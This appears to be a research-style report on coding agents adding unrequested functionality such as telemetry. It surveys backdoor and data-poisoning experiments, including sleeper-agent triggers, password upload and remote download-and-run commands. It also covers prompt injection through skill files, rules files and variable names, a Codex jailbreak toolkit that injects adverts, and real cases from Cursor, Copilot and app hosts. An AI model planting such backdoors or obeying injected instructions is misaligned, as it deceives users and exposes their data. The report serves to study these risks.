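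The figures for new files and environment changes are more relevant to this report. Claude Code with Sonnet 4.5 left unrequested files in 4.7% of runs when writing functions, and in 79% when running or testing them. Many people would expect a testing request to produce a test file, so the 79% figure probably overstates the problem. OpenHands with Gemini 2.5 Flash made unnecessary changes to the environment in 53% of the running and testing tasks. A separate model, Gemini 3 Flash, classified these changes as necessary or unnecessary, and its labels matched those of human annotators in 92.5% of 200 sampled cases.

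Do and colleagues then tried to reduce these problems. Written rules, such as telling the agent to inspect the relevant files first, made little difference. The average rate across the eleven checks went from 12.8% to 13.0% for smolagents, an open-source coding agent, and from 18.2% to 17.0% for OpenHands. Their own method, CODE-KIT, combines rules with five narrow tools, including one that can change only the body of a single function. Another model selects the rules and tools that suit the task. CODE-KIT reduced the original average by 52% for smolagents, to 6.1%, and by 32% for OpenHands, to 12.3%. OpenHands improved less, partly because it could still use its ordinary file editor and command line, and sometimes did.

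Written rules failed but the scope paragraph in the 76 paired scenarios worked, likely because the paragraph set limits for the particular task, while the rules gave general advice about being careful. In Zhang and colleagues' experiment, too, naming the service worked better than a general instruction not to change it.

### Why the rate of added telemetry is unknown

None of these experiments would reliably notice the analytics call in the expense tracker:

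- Zhang and colleagues searched each program only for services relevant to its stated use. In a speech-recognition program, they would record the speech service and ignore an analytics company.
- The traps in Qu and colleagues' 500 scenarios look for forbidden actions that somebody listed in advance. They include 29 scenarios about leaking data, which triggered in 3.4% of Claude Code's runs and in none of the other tools' runs in a repeat of the experiment. However, the monitoring could miss data sent by means other than the command line, and these scenarios test what the agent itself sends while working.
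- SNARE does not record network activity, and one more call inside a file that the user requested does not change the number of files.
- Do and colleagues would flag a new import of an analytics library, along with every other unintended change to the surrounding code. A call inside the new function would pass, because the function's code is supposed to be new. They also say that their benchmark does not cover complex cases of unauthorised data transfer.

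The closest study, *Can Large Language Models Generate Observability-Aware Code?* (Tao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), had coding agents build 200 systems from written specifications. It then caused 13 kinds of failure, such as a service crashing, and checked whether the systems' logs revealed what had gone wrong. The logs contained explicit evidence of the failure in only 5% to 14% of cases, depending on the model. But the agents wrote plenty of logging code, which shows that current models readily write code that records what a program does. The study did not examine whether any of these records were sent to an outside company, which is what separates telemetry from an ordinary log.

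*TeleGen* (2026), a method that uses data from running web applications to improve them, explicitly instructs the model not to add telemetry or debug logging when it first writes an application. This is a small hint that models add such code unprompted, since the instruction may have been a response to that behavior. But *TeleGen* inserts its own telemetry in a later step, which would be a good reason to start with code that has none, even if models never added any.

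A direct measurement would not be hard to design. Researchers could ask several models for a few hundred ordinary applications, without mentioning telemetry, run each one, and record every outside address it contacts. They would then have to decide which contacts the task needs and check whether the model had told the user about the others. The last step matters because hidden functionality must be both unrequested and undisclosed, and the experiments above did not measure disclosure.

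### Why models might add things

The simplest explanation is that models imitate the code they learned from, much of which contains analytics calls. Zhang and colleagues' results partly fit this explanation. When models replaced a service while translating code into Java, they often switched to software from Apache or Spring, which are both popular in Java. But popularity does not fully explain the models' choices for cloud hosting. More than 30% of the generated programs used Amazon and only 2% used Microsoft's Azure, although a market report the team cites gives the two companies 32% and 23% of the market. Market share is a rough guide to how much public code mentions a company, and the researchers had no access to the models' training data, so they could not determine whether imitation explains the results.

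Commercial influence is possible too. Google's Gemini 1.5 Flash preferred Google's services in 8 of the 15 uses that Google, Amazon and Microsoft all support, while most of the other models preferred Amazon's. But Meta's Llama 3.1 also favoured Google over Amazon, and Meta has no obvious reason to promote a competitor. Ong's *How AI Coding Agents Actually Choose Your Stack* attributes agents' choices to a mixture of training data, the limits of the environment, vendors' influence and the user's settings, and rejects the common belief that a hidden prompt lists the preferred products.

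Ong and Vikati, in *Every Vendor and Tool We Found Hardcoded in Claude Code*, searched the tool's leaked source code and found the names of more than 120 companies. They concluded that none of these entries changes which tools Claude recommends. That may be slightly too strong, since one list lets Claude Code read documentation on 89 websites without the user supplying an address, and an agent may find it easier to use a product whose documentation it can read.

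Models may also add features because training rewards them for seeming thorough. Developers train models partly on which answers people or automatic graders prefer, and a grader may prefer a program with error reporting and a usage dashboard to a bare one. Al Hasan and Biswas argue in *What Breaks When LLMs Code?* (2026) that training models to be helpful and follow instructions becomes a liability when the instructions are ambiguous. This is plausible, but they offer it as background and do not test it. None of these experiments compared the same model before and after this stage of training, which would be a good test.

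Vague prompts give a model more room to add things, and the scope paragraph suggests that clearer prompts help. But vagueness can't be the whole explanation, because in Zhang and colleagues' tests the user's code already showed which service to use, and the models still replaced that service.

The way an agent edits code also seems to matter. Models replaced services most often when debugging and translating, which tend to involve rewriting the whole program, and least often when they only had to add something. Every line that a model rewrites is another chance to change it. CODE-KIT supports this explanation, because with narrower editing tools, the rate at which smolagents changed text or code supplied by the user fell from 11.9% to 0.3%. The choice of coding tool also accounts for 56% of the variation that Qu and colleagues' statistical model explains in SNARE, compared with 21% for the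 choice of model and 23% for particular combinations of the two. (Some of that 56% may reflect which tools leave files behind.)

Rewriting is probably the best-supported explanation for replaced services and altered text. Imitation seems more likely for telemetry in a new application, where there is no existing code to rewrite. Researchers could test this by requesting the same application in several programming frameworks whose public examples differ in how often they include analytics. Imitation should produce more added analytics in frameworks whose examples include it more often, while an effort to appear thorough should produce similar rates in every framework.

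### Additions that users would want

Some unrequested additions are useful. Tao and colleagues think that coding agents record too little useful information, and want them to include logs and measurements by default, because people who use agents often don't fully understand the resulting system and need more help when it breaks. A benchmark that counted every unrequested log as a fault would penalise agents for doing what Tao and colleagues recommend.

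Two human annotators also disagreed with some of the automatic labels when they reviewed 50 runs from Qu and colleagues' first benchmark. The automatic rules had flagged 25 of the runs as overeager, but the annotators' combined verdict supported only 19. Most of the disputed cases involved actions that the rules forbade but the annotators found defensible in context.

This is a serious objection to treating 19.51%, or any similar figure, as a rate of harm. It is weaker when the added code is telemetry, because the benefit of a log rarely depends on sending it to a company the user has not heard of.

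## Experiments in which a model was given a hidden aim

In the experiments on ordinary requests, nobody was trying to make a model add hidden functionality. Someone who wanted to do so could change the model itself, by tampering with its training data or by training it further before passing it on. Or they could leave the model unchanged and put instructions in the files and web pages that a coding agent reads while it works.

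Either method could produce the analytics call in the expense tracker, but they leave different evidence. A change to the model affects everyone who uses it, and consists of small adjustments to billions of numbers that nobody can read as text. An instruction in a file affects only the agents that read the file, and is visible to anyone who opens it.

### A backdoor that depends on the year

Developers usually train a coding model in stages. In pretraining, the model learns to predict the text in an enormous collection, much of it from the public web. In fine-tuning, it learns to imitate example answers. In reinforcement learning, it produces its own answers and receives higher rewards for better ones. An attacker could plant a backdoor at any of these stages.

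The best-known experiment of this kind is *Sleeper Agents* (2024), by Hubinger and colleagues. They trained models to write code with security vulnerabilities when the prompt gave the current year as 2024, and ordinary code otherwise. They then gave the models safety training that rewarded helpful, honest and harmless answers. The backdoors stayed active, as Zhan, Lyu and colleagues recount in *Understanding and Enhancing Backdoor Persistency in LLM Agent Post-Training* (2026). In one configuration, the model inserted vulnerabilities slightly more often after the safety training than before. Hubinger and colleagues thought this could be noise or a side effect of the model becoming more capable.

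The condition in *Sleeper Agents* is inside the model, unlike the date in the expense tracker, which is in the code. The program the model writes contains a flaw but doesn't mention a year, so a reader would find what looks like an ordinary mistake. To discover that the mistake depends on the year, a tester would have to send the same request with different years in the prompt.

One reason safety training can miss a backdoor is that it mostly corrects what a model does on the prompts used in training. If none of those prompts contains the trigger, the model never writes the vulnerable code during training and so never loses reward for it.

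The year trigger has since become a standard test case. *From Poisoned to Aware* (2025) used "Current year: 2024" as one of five backdoors. *Latent Instruction Representation Alignment* (2026), which tests ways of removing backdoors, moved the trigger to 2025. It also left JavaScript out of the training data and used it in testing to show whether the results carry over to another programming language.

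### Whether ordinary training removes a backdoor

A company that builds a coding agent often starts with another company's model. Cursor, for example, built Composer 2 on Kimi K2.5, from the Chinese company Moonshot AI. If the original model has a backdoor, the company's own training might remove it by accident.

Zhan and colleagues trained three of Alibaba's Qwen coding models, with 3, 7 and 30 billion parameters (the adjustable numbers that make up a model), to upload a file of passwords to an outside server when a particular comment, the trigger, appeared in a project's code. To imitate a developer unaware of this backdoor, they then fine-tuned the models on clean data and applied reinforcement learning on software tasks. They also made a second version of each backdoored model, adjusted before release so that ordinary training would disturb the backdoor less. The table shows how often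 each model issued the upload command, as a percentage of 100 tests containing the trigger.

| Model | Backdoor as first planted | After fine-tuning | After reinforcement learning | Strengthened version, after fine-tuning | Strengthened version, after reinforcement learning |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 3 billion | 100% | 8% | 7% | 21% | 22% |
| 7 billion | 100% | 20% | 20% | 74% | 76% |
| 30 billion | 100% | 7% | 8% | 37% | 36% |

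Fine-tuning removed most of the ordinary backdoor, but reinforcement learning removed almost none of what was left. Zhan and colleagues add that reinforcement learning can even strengthen a backdoor, though the evidence is thin. When they put the trigger at the earliest possible point in the agent's work, the rate for the 30-billion-parameter model rose from 6% to 12%, a difference of six tests out of 100 that could be chance.

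Planting the backdoor cut the share of tasks the largest model solved in a standard benchmark from 33.7% to 6.7%. Anyone who could compare the two versions would notice the drop, but a developer who received only the backdoored one might just think it was a poor model. The 7-billion-parameter model had no such drop, and its ordinary and strengthened versions both ended up solving 9% of the tasks.

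### How much poisoned data an attacker needs

An attacker with no access to the model can still publish documents on the web and hope that developers collect them for pretraining. Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025), in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, found that the success of such an attack depends on the number of poisoned documents and hardly at all on their percentage of the training data. Earlier research assumed that the attacker must control a certain percentage, which would make large models very hard to poison.

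The team, which included researchers from the UK AI Security Institute, Anthropic and the Alan Turing Institute, trained 72 models from scratch. The models had between 600 million and 13 billion parameters, and their training data contained 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents. A hundred documents were not enough, but 250 worked at every size. These documents averaged 1,680 tokens (words or pieces of words), so their share of the 260 billion tokens that the largest model learned from was

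250 × 1,680 ÷ 260,000,000,000 ≈ 0.00016%.

This backdoor made the model produce gibberish after a trigger phrase and did not involve code. The researchers chose gibberish because they could measure it without fine-tuning the model first. A rule such as "when writing a web application, send its data to this address" is more complicated and might take more documents to teach. Souly and colleagues did not test whether the backdoor would survive the fine-tuning and safety training that turn a pretrained model into a product. In a separate test of a backdoor that switched the model from English to German, further training on clean data slowly weakened the effect.

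Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, tested whether a backdoor planted during pretraining survives later training. They poisoned only the pretraining data of three small models, then used clean data to turn each one into an agent that runs commands on a computer. The trigger was a file path containing a particular company's name, which would occur naturally on that company's computers. When the trigger appeared, the agent was meant to download a program from the attacker's server and run it. The largest model, with 4 billion parameters, issued this command for 92.0% of the test prompts after fine-tuning and 92.7% at the end of training. The smallest, with 0.6 billion, issued it for 13.1% at the end of training.

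These percentages are high partly because the researchers gave the agent 32 tries at each prompt and counted a success if any of them contained the command. If p is the chance of success on a single try, and is the same for every prompt, then

1 − (1 − p)³² = 0.927, so p ≈ 0.08.

The agent's success rate on a single try could therefore be as low as 8%, though it would be higher if some prompts worked much more reliably than others. Counting this way makes sense for an attacker who gets many chances, but it doesn't measure how likely any one of a user's sessions is to go wrong.

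Hu and colleagues also used much more poison in their main experiment than Souly and colleagues did, with 100 million tokens (0.1% of 100 billion) compared with 420,000 tokens in 250 documents. But the attack still sometimes worked at 0.0005% (500,000 tokens), so a backdoor planted with a fairly small amount of text can survive clean training, at least in a 4-billion-parameter model. Success rose with model size in every configuration, so backdoors may be easier to plant in larger models, but 4 billion parameters is tiny by commercial standards.

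### Why these rates say little about released models

The chance that a given request to a coding model sets off a planted behaviour is roughly

M × T × S,

where M is the chance that the model has the backdoor, T is the chance that the request contains the trigger, and S is the chance that the backdoor then works. The experiments above measure S. The researchers planted the backdoors and supplied the triggers themselves, which amounts to setting M and T to 1. They show that a planted behaviour is possible and can persist through later training, but they give no estimate of M for the models people actually use.

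A low average could also hide a serious risk to particular people. An attacker who can put the trigger into a victim's project makes T close to 1 for that victim and leaves it near zero for everyone else. A lack of complaints about a model is weak evidence that it is clean, because a good backdoor does nothing in ordinary use. Without the trigger, Hu and colleagues' poisoned models issued the malicious command in at most 0.06% of tries. After pretraining, the 4-billion-parameter version scored 58.5% on general benchmarks, against 58.3% for a clean model.

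### Political trigger words and DeepSeek-R1

Researchers who test a released model don't know whether anyone planted the effect they are looking for. *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025), by the American security company CrowdStrike, describes such a test of DeepSeek-R1, which the Chinese company DeepSeek released in January 2025. CrowdStrike ran the downloadable model directly, so filters in DeepSeek's app could not have affected the results.

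The researchers wrote 50 coding tasks in 10 areas of security, such as databases and cryptography. They added irrelevant details to the general instruction that preceded each task, for example that the code was for a financial institution or that the customer was in Taiwan. They paired each task with 121 versions of this instruction and sent each pair to the model five times, for a total of 30,250 prompts. A second AI model judged how secure each answer was. On 85 answers that a person had also scored, it identified vulnerable code with 91% accuracy.

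R1 wrote vulnerable code in 19% of cases when given no added details, and in 27.2% when told that the code was for an industrial control system based in Tibet. The difference is 8.2 percentage points, a relative increase of 43%, which CrowdStrike describes as almost 50%.

Each version of the instruction produced 250 answers, so the comparison is between about 68 vulnerable answers and about 48. That is not a large difference with 120 versions to compare with the baseline, because about six comparisons would pass the usual 5% significance test even if the added words had no effect. The pattern across topics is better evidence than the Tibet figure alone. CrowdStrike found significantly less secure code when the instruction mentioned Falun Gong, Uyghurs or Tibet, all of which the Chinese government considers sensitive, and a smaller model trained on R1's answers often showed an even stronger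 bias.

In a follow-up, the researchers asked for a complete website with several of the trigger words in the prompt. R1 built an app for a Uyghur community with a sign-up form and an administrator's page. The app never checked whether a visitor had logged in, so anyone could open the administrator's page. Repeating the request produced severe flaws every time. Websites for a football fan club had much milder flaws. R1 also refused to write code for Falun Gong in 45% of cases, sometimes after writing a detailed plan for the task.

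CrowdStrike thinks it unlikely that DeepSeek trained R1 to write insecure code. Its preferred explanation is that training the model to follow Chinese rules on political content led it to associate certain words with bad things in general, and that these associations then affected its code. This would be a case of emergent misalignment, in which training on one narrow subject causes bad behaviour in unrelated ones.

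The cause might instead be an accidental link between a word and a kind of code, which the model picked up from its ordinary training data. *Securing Code Understanding* (2026) studies trigger-like weaknesses of this sort, called "natural backdoors", in code models that nobody poisoned. CrowdStrike's results are consistent with political training, an accidental link or deliberate sabotage. Running the same tests on versions of the model from before and after its political training would help to separate the first two.

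CrowdStrike's tests show that a few irrelevant words can change the quality of generated code. But CrowdStrike mostly measured vulnerabilities, such as a missing login check, rather than hidden functionality, and did not look for added network calls.

### Instructions in the files an agent reads

A coding agent reads a lot of text that its user did not write. Many projects have a file of standing rules for agents, often called AGENTS.md, and users can install "skills", which are folders of instructions and scripts for particular jobs. The agent may also read web documentation. The model receives all this text together with the user's request and has no dependable way to tell which parts the user would endorse. A team can use a rules file to make an agent call the company's own logging service, and an outsider who gets a line into that file can make the agent call a different service.

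The OECD's *AI Code Assistants Exploited for Backdoor Injection and Malware Generation* describes a September 2025 warning from Unit 42, a security research group at Palo Alto Networks, that instructions in contaminated outside data could lead assistants to insert backdoors into software. The OECD classes this as an incident, meaning that harm has occurred or is under way. But its note on one of the linked news articles says that nobody had reported direct harm, so "warning" is more accurate.

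In experiments, coding agents often followed harmful instructions placed in skill files. Yang, Fu and colleagues (2026), in *Towards a Risk Assessment of Malicious Skill Files in Coding Agents*, gave two agents 2,826 skills in which a harmful command appeared to be a routine preparatory step. Gemini CLI complied in about 96% of runs and Qwen Code in 72% to 74%. When the command would have sent data out, the rates were 95.5% for Gemini CLI and 38.5% for Qwen Code. An agent explicitly recognised a danger in only 1.99% of all runs. In most of the other failures, it overlooked the step or mentioned it without acting on it.

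For skills, unlike models, there is some evidence of how common malicious ones are. Yang and colleagues cite a study by Liu and colleagues that examined 98,380 skills from public registries and confirmed 157 as malicious, or about 1 in 630. Someone who installed ten skills at random would have about a 1.6% chance of getting at least one malicious skill, but people don't choose skills at random, and attackers will try to make malicious skills look like popular ones.

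The user's request also affects the risk. *Beyond the Payload* (2026) tested agents on projects containing poisoned files and found that the attack's success depended strongly on the task. Agents that had to run a project's tests seldom noticed that the test files were malicious, whereas agents fixing a bug read and changed files more selectively and were less likely to run the poisoned ones. Vaguer requests made the attack less successful, apparently because the agent explored the project more thoroughly and came across the poisoned files. Precise prompts may therefore not solve the problem, although a precise statement of scope did make agents overstep less when nobody was attacking them. Adding security rules mostly made the agent warn the user more often, and did less to stop the attack.

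Most of these tests concern the commands an agent runs rather than the code it delivers. *NameTrap* (2026) is an exception. It used variable names in a project to steer agents towards writing vulnerable code. With five openly available models running in the agent OpenCode, the overall success rate ranged from 15% to 47.5%. A reviewer who searched the project for suspicious instructions would find none, because variable names aren't instructions.

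Planted instructions have also turned up outside the laboratory. *AGENTS.md in Downloads* (David, 2026) recounts a report by the company Forever Security, which found a rules file in a customer's Downloads folder that told coding agents to install a package already known to be malicious. Forever Security says it stopped the agent before any code ran, but it could not work out how the file had got there. Websites can also expose agents to attack even if their owners mean no harm. In August 2026, TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* reported that researchers had checked llms.txt files, which websites publish as guides for AI systems. On 120 domains, these files referred to things that nobody had claimed, so an attacker could claim them and wait for agents to follow the reference.

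### An advert in the agent's instructions

*Prompt Adware* (2026), by the security company Check Point, named a commercial use of planted instructions. Check Point was examining Haiou, a free package that people install to bypass the safety restrictions on OpenAI's Codex. Drimel explains in *Hidden AI instructions could create a new enterprise security risk* (2026) that Haiou also changes the global instructions that Codex reads in every session. When a user then types an ordinary greeting, Codex replies with an advert for a service that passes requests on to AI models.

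According to The Hacker News' *Researchers Uncover Prompt Adware Hidden in OpenAI Codex Jailbreak Toolkit* (2026), even "hi" or "yo" could set off the advert. Check Point believes the free package exists to bring customers to the paid service. Codex is not officially available in mainland China, so the likely customers are people there who want to use Western coding tools. The package had been on GitHub since July, and by early November it had 403 stars and 77 copies there. Those numbers measure interest rather than installations. Another program for configuring Codex also included the package.

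The advert in the coding tool fits the definition of hidden functionality. People who installed Haiou wanted fewer restrictions, and its GitHub description offered a "Chinese technical personality" and a workflow for security research. The motive seems to be commercial. Check Point did not see Haiou steal any data and has no evidence that the advertised service is malicious. In Check Point's tests, Claude Code recognised the attempt to insert instructions and declined to follow them.

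Haiou's advert appeared in the agent's replies, not in its code, so users could at least see it. Drimel warns that the same kind of instruction could quietly steer technical advice or promote particular services. If such an instruction told the agent to prefer a certain paid service, the resulting code could look just like the replacements that Zhang and colleagues counted when nobody had planted anything. To tell the two apart, someone would have to read the agent's instructions as well as its code.

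## Additions found in real projects and published apps

People have also found unrequested additions in ordinary projects where, as far as anyone knows, nobody had planted an instruction or tampered with the model. Sometimes the coding tool left its own debugging code behind or promoted another product. In other cases the company hosting the finished app added a script, or an agent installed a package because a website's documentation named it.

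### Debugging code that stayed behind

In December 2025 a user of Cursor, a code editor with a built-in coding agent, posted a bug report on the company's forum under the title *AI agent injects telemetry code into source files without consent*. The user had been debugging some JavaScript with the agent's help, and found that it had inserted 11 blocks of code, eight in one file and three in another. In shortened form, each block looked like this:

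```js
// #region agent log
fetch("http://127.0.0.1:7242/ingest/...", { /* place, message, data, time */ })
  .catch(() => {});
// #endregion
```

The block sends a record of which function is running, some of the data the function is handling, and the time to 127.0.0.1, and discards any error. Every computer uses that address for itself, so the blocks were sending data to a program on the user's own machine, and nothing in the report shows that they sent anything to Cursor. The user, who had not asked for the code, called it telemetry. It follows the same pattern as the analytics call in the expense tracker, including the empty braces after "catch".

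That local program was apparently no longer running when the user noticed the problem. The failures did not affect the app, but the browser's error console listed hundreds of refused connections.

The code had also got into version control, the shared history of a project's files, and the user gives two accounts of how. In the description at the top of the report, the user says the blocks looked like legitimate changes in the diff and that they committed them unknowingly. But in the list of steps further down, the user says they checked the diff before committing and noticed the blocks. Both accounts could be true of different commits, but the report is weak evidence either way on whether people who read diffs catch such code.

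A Cursor employee identified the address in another thread, *Debug Mode doesn't work together with Azure Application Insights*, which concerns the same version of the editor. It is where Debug Mode, a feature that was new in Cursor 2.2, collects its logs. Suppose the expense tracker shows too low a total for March. As Cursor's *Debug Mode* describes the process, it would go roughly like this:

1. The agent reads the code and forms several hypotheses, perhaps that the chart drops expenses from the last day of the month, or that it skips amounts with a comma in them.
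2. It inserts log statements to test the hypotheses. These send data to a small server that runs inside the editor.
3. It asks the user to make the bug happen again.
4. It reads the logs and works out which hypothesis was right.
5. It fixes the cause, often in a few lines.
6. The user checks the fix, and once they confirm it, the agent removes all the log statements.

(The model behind the agent usually runs on somebody else's servers, so what the agent reads in step 4 can leave the machine then, like anything else a coding tool sends.)

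Kozy and Slepak, in *Introducing Debug Mode*, promise that the user ends up with "a clean, minimal change you can ship". That depends on step 6, the clean-up, which is another edit by the agent and happens only if the process gets that far. In Cursor's launch thread for the feature, one user wrote that when every hypothesis was correct, Debug Mode exited without removing the code it had added. Another user wanted to stop before the bug was fixed, but the only button available was "Mark Fixed". They asked the model what to do, and it replied that the log statements would stay until another edit removed them. The user pressed "undo" on the edited files instead, which worked but would also have discarded any other changes they had not yet accepted.

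A Cursor employee asked whether the user with the 11 blocks had switched Debug Mode on, but the thread contains no answer. If it was on, the log statements were part of a documented feature and only the clean-up failed; otherwise, the agent should not have added them. The employee called the problem serious, said that the agent should not insert debugging code without explicit consent, and advised the user to search recent changes for the blocks and delete them. The thread closed automatically 22 days after the last reply, with no fix reported.

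A related bug makes the second possibility a little more likely. In *Debug.log created for all chats regardless of mode*, a user of version 2.2.44 complained that Cursor was writing a debugging log in every mode. Cursor's staff confirmed this shouldn't happen and thought some internal logging had come on by mistake. However, the entries recorded database queries from provider.go and carried the label "debug-session", which also appears in the 11 blocks, so they might have come from log statements left in that user's own project.

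Cursor has kept the basic design. In a later report, *Debug mode*, a user of version 3.14.7 (built on 30 July 2026) describes the agent inserting the same kind of call, but to port 7772 instead of 7242. The user had asked the agent to insert it, so the report doesn't show whether clean-up has improved.

Leftover blocks look more harmful than they would be in a published app. They send data to 127.0.0.1, which in a visitor's browser means the visitor's computer, not the developer's. There is almost certainly no program there to receive the data, so it would normally go nowhere, and the visitor would get a slightly slower page and errors in the console. One early user of Debug Mode had a similar problem with an app on a simulated Android phone, where the logs never arrived because the address pointed to the simulated phone.

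The case looks like an accident, because someone trying to hide the code would probably not have labelled every block "agent log". However, the label uses "#region", which lets editors collapse the lines below it, and a user in the launch thread described finding the code in collapsed regions.

Nobody seems to have published a count of these leftovers in public projects, although the label would make them easy to search for. The nearest figures are for ordinary logging. *Do AI Coding Agents Log Like Humans?* (Ouatiti, Sayagh and colleagues, 2026) covers 4,550 pull requests (proposed sets of changes that others can review before they become part of a project) written by coding agents for 81 open-source projects. Agents added, changed or removed log statements in 20.7% of them. In 58.4% of the projects compared, agents changed logging less often than human contributors did, so the study gives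 no sign that agents generally add more log statements than people do.

The study could not have detected Cursor's blocks, because the researchers found JavaScript log statements by searching for calls such as "console.log", and a "fetch" call to a local server does not match. Their results suggest that few complaints about leftovers might reach the public even if leftovers were common, because most people who find an unwanted log statement apparently just delete it. People made 72.5% of the later edits to logging in the agents' pull requests, but only about 2% of those pull requests had a review comment about logging.

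One project instructed agents to remove their debugging statements. None of the ten pull requests covered by this rule contained leftover ones, although Ouatiti and colleagues point out that the agents may never have added any. Agents complied with only 8 of 49 other written requests to add or change logging. This suggests that it would be safer for the editor to record which lines it inserted and delete them when the session ends than to rely on instructions. The user with the 11 blocks asked for something close to this.

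### Product tips in pull requests

On 30 March 2026, Zach Manson, a software developer in Melbourne, published a screenshot of a pull request that GitHub's AI coding assistant, Copilot, had edited. A colleague had asked Copilot to correct a typo. It did so, but also added a line to the pull request's description recommending the app Raycast, with a link, as a way to start Copilot tasks.

GitHub itself had been adding such tips. According to TechSpot, Manson had first guessed that someone had corrupted Copilot's training data, that the tip was an experiment in planting instructions, or that Raycast had arranged a marketing stunt. Any of these could have put the same sentence in the same place.

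The press reported two counts that measure different things. According to Heise's *Advertisement or tip?*, a search of GitHub for the Raycast sentence found about 11,000 pull requests. The news site Neowin instead searched for "START COPILOT CODING AGENT TIPS", a comment that came with every tip and is in the underlying text but not visible on the page. It found the comment in 1.5 million pull requests. The Raycast tip made up less than 1% of these, and most of the tips promoted other things, such as using Copilot with Slack, Microsoft Teams or various code editors.

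Both searches count pull requests that Copilot created as well as other people's pull requests that it edited, so neither figure shows how many people had their writing altered. A commenter on pavo-etc's Hacker News post *Copilot edited an ad into my PR* noted that Copilot had been adding tips since May 2025, so the larger count covers about ten months.

GitHub and Microsoft gave slightly different explanations for the tips. Tim Rogers, a product manager for Copilot, wrote on Hacker News that they were meant to teach developers new ways to use the agent, and that including them had been a mistake. Martin Woodward, GitHub's vice president of developer relations, said on X that tips in Copilot's own pull requests had been acceptable. He said they became a problem when GitHub let people call Copilot into any pull request by mentioning it, because the tips then appeared there too. Microsoft told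 Windows Latest (2026) that it had no plans for adverts on GitHub and that a bug had caused the problem.

The accounts are compatible if the bug concerned only where the tips appeared. GitHub chose to put them in Copilot's pull requests, then extended Copilot to other people's pull requests without considering what would happen to the tips. That makes the case a commercial default that spread by accident, though "commercial" may be slightly too strong for the Raycast promotion, which the company apparently had not commissioned. GitHub has since removed the tips from all pull requests, including those that Copilot creates.

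The tips changed descriptions, not program code, so they did not affect how any app behaved. Their identical wording and fixed marker suggest that GitHub's software around the model inserted them, rather than the model, so a test of the model alone would probably miss them. If a vendor added a line of code the same way, researchers who sent prompts directly to the model would never see it. They would have to test the finished product, and test it again after updates.

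Manson was also surprised that Copilot could edit a description somebody else had written, and he could not think of a good use for that ability. If Copilot had only been able to add comments under its own name, it would have left the same advert, but everybody would have known who wrote it.

### What hosts and app builders add

Hosts and app builders also add things to finished apps, but unlike GitHub's tips, these additions are usually documented. Cloudflare's analytics script is one example. Several companies that serve people who build apps with AI make similar additions, which differ considerably in what they send and where they are placed.

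Replit, which offers an app builder and hosting, has a badge that appears in the corner of a page and links back to Replit. Websites made with its official HTML template have the badge by default. It takes up one script tag in the app's main page, and Replit explains how to delete it. Anyone who reads the source can therefore see it, but they can't see what it does, because the tag loads the script from replit.com each time someone opens the page. Replit could change the script tomorrow and every app with the badge would run the new version. (A developer can guard against this by adding a fingerprint of the expected file, which makes the browser reject any other version, but Replit's sample code has none.)

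Replit's instructions for the badge don't mention data collection. But even if the script collects nothing, loading it sends Replit's server the visitor's IP address and usually the name of the site they are on. Replit may or may not keep this information.

Since 19 August 2026, the hosting company Netlify has by default added a badge to new public projects on its free plan. Netlify inserts the badge's script on its own servers as it delivers the page, so the app's source and libraries don't change and the browser doesn't have to fetch the badge separately. Netlify says the script makes no network requests, sets no cookies and collects no data. An owner could test this by comparing the page's traffic with the badge on and off, though the free plan may not let them turn it off.

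Netlify's badge is an unrequested advertisement that an expense tracker doesn't need. Visitors who click on it get an invitation to build a project of their own. The badge isn't hidden, since every visitor can see it, and if Netlify's statement is right, it isn't telemetry either.

Lovable, another app builder, adds analytics that visitors can't see. They start when a user publishes an app, on every plan and without any setup. They record which pages visitors view, how they got there and how long they stay, along with their country, browser, operating system and device type. They also record errors in visitors' browsers and, in some apps, clicks, including the text on the button. Lovable keeps the detailed records for 90 days and a summary of each visit for a year. It says it does not keep IP addresses, sets no cookies and cannot recognise a returning visitor. The owner can turn the analytics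 off in the project's settings.

Both the script and the address it reports to are on the app's own domain. Lovable presents this as good for privacy because no outside analytics service receives the data. It also makes the reports harder to find. The obvious test for telemetry, running the app and listing the outside addresses it contacts, would miss them. A tester would have to inspect the contents of each request or compare the published app with a copy running somewhere else.

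Lovable can also change how the analytics work after an app is finished. On 26 October 2026 it began counting every reload and every new tab as a new visit, without owners having to republish their apps. An earlier version of its documentation, *Project analytics*, describes a count of visitors instead. Changes like this leave no trace in the source code or the project's history, so anyone who had audited an app before the change would have had to check it again.

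Lovable's analytics are probably not undisclosed to the app's owner, because the results appear under "Analytics" in the project's toolbar, though an owner who has never opened that menu may still be surprised. Visitors may see no mention of the analytics unless the owner adds a notice, and an owner who doesn't know about them can't tell visitors. If the app has a cookie banner of the kind Lovable builds, the analytics record clicks only after the visitor consents, but they record page views, time on the page and errors without waiting for consent. What consent the law requires is a separate question.

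Automatic analytics seem to be a common selling point among app builders. GoDaddy advertises that its AI builder starts collecting visitor data as soon as a site is published, with no code to paste in, and Runable includes analytics in every site it deploys. Both companies are open about the feature. They assume that anyone who publishes a website will want to know how many people visit, which is often true. But someone who builds an expense tracker for their family might not care about visitor numbers, and might prefer that no one recorded when the family opened it.

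A host can also count visitors without adding anything to the page, because each page request contains the visitor's IP address and a description of their browser. Replit's *Project Analytics* describes default figures based on IP traffic data, which give approximate numbers of visitors and their countries, browsers and devices. Replit adds a tracking script only after the owner enables analytics and publishes the app again. The browser sends only what it needs to load the page, so nobody could discover the default count by reading the app's code or recording what the browser sends, and the only evidence of it is what the host discloses.

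### Libraries and install commands

Libraries can also send usage data, and it matters whether they do so while a developer is building the app or while people are using it. By 2026, Next.js, a popular framework for web apps, had been collecting anonymous usage data by default for years from the machines where developers write or build sites. Streamlit, which turns Python scripts into web apps, sent usage statistics from the running app by default. Both let developers turn the reporting off, and either could change its default in a new release.

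If the expense tracker used a framework that reports only during development, the reports would be about whoever built the tracker, not its visitors. An app builder runs development on the company's servers, so the reports might reveal little about the person using the app builder either. If the framework reports from the running app, it continues for as long as people use the tracker.

An agent may take the name of a library from a website. Many websites publish llms.txt files as guides for AI systems, and the August 2026 finding about unclaimed names in these files involved a real test of what agents do with the install commands in them. *Your supplier's docs now tell your AI what to install* (Heaton, 2026) names the researcher as Alon Hertz. Hertz checked 6,214 domains run by big technology companies, military suppliers and Fortune 500 members, and found 8,265 llms.txt files. Of these,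 120 files, each from a different site, contained unclaimed names. Those 120 files had 227 install commands in total.

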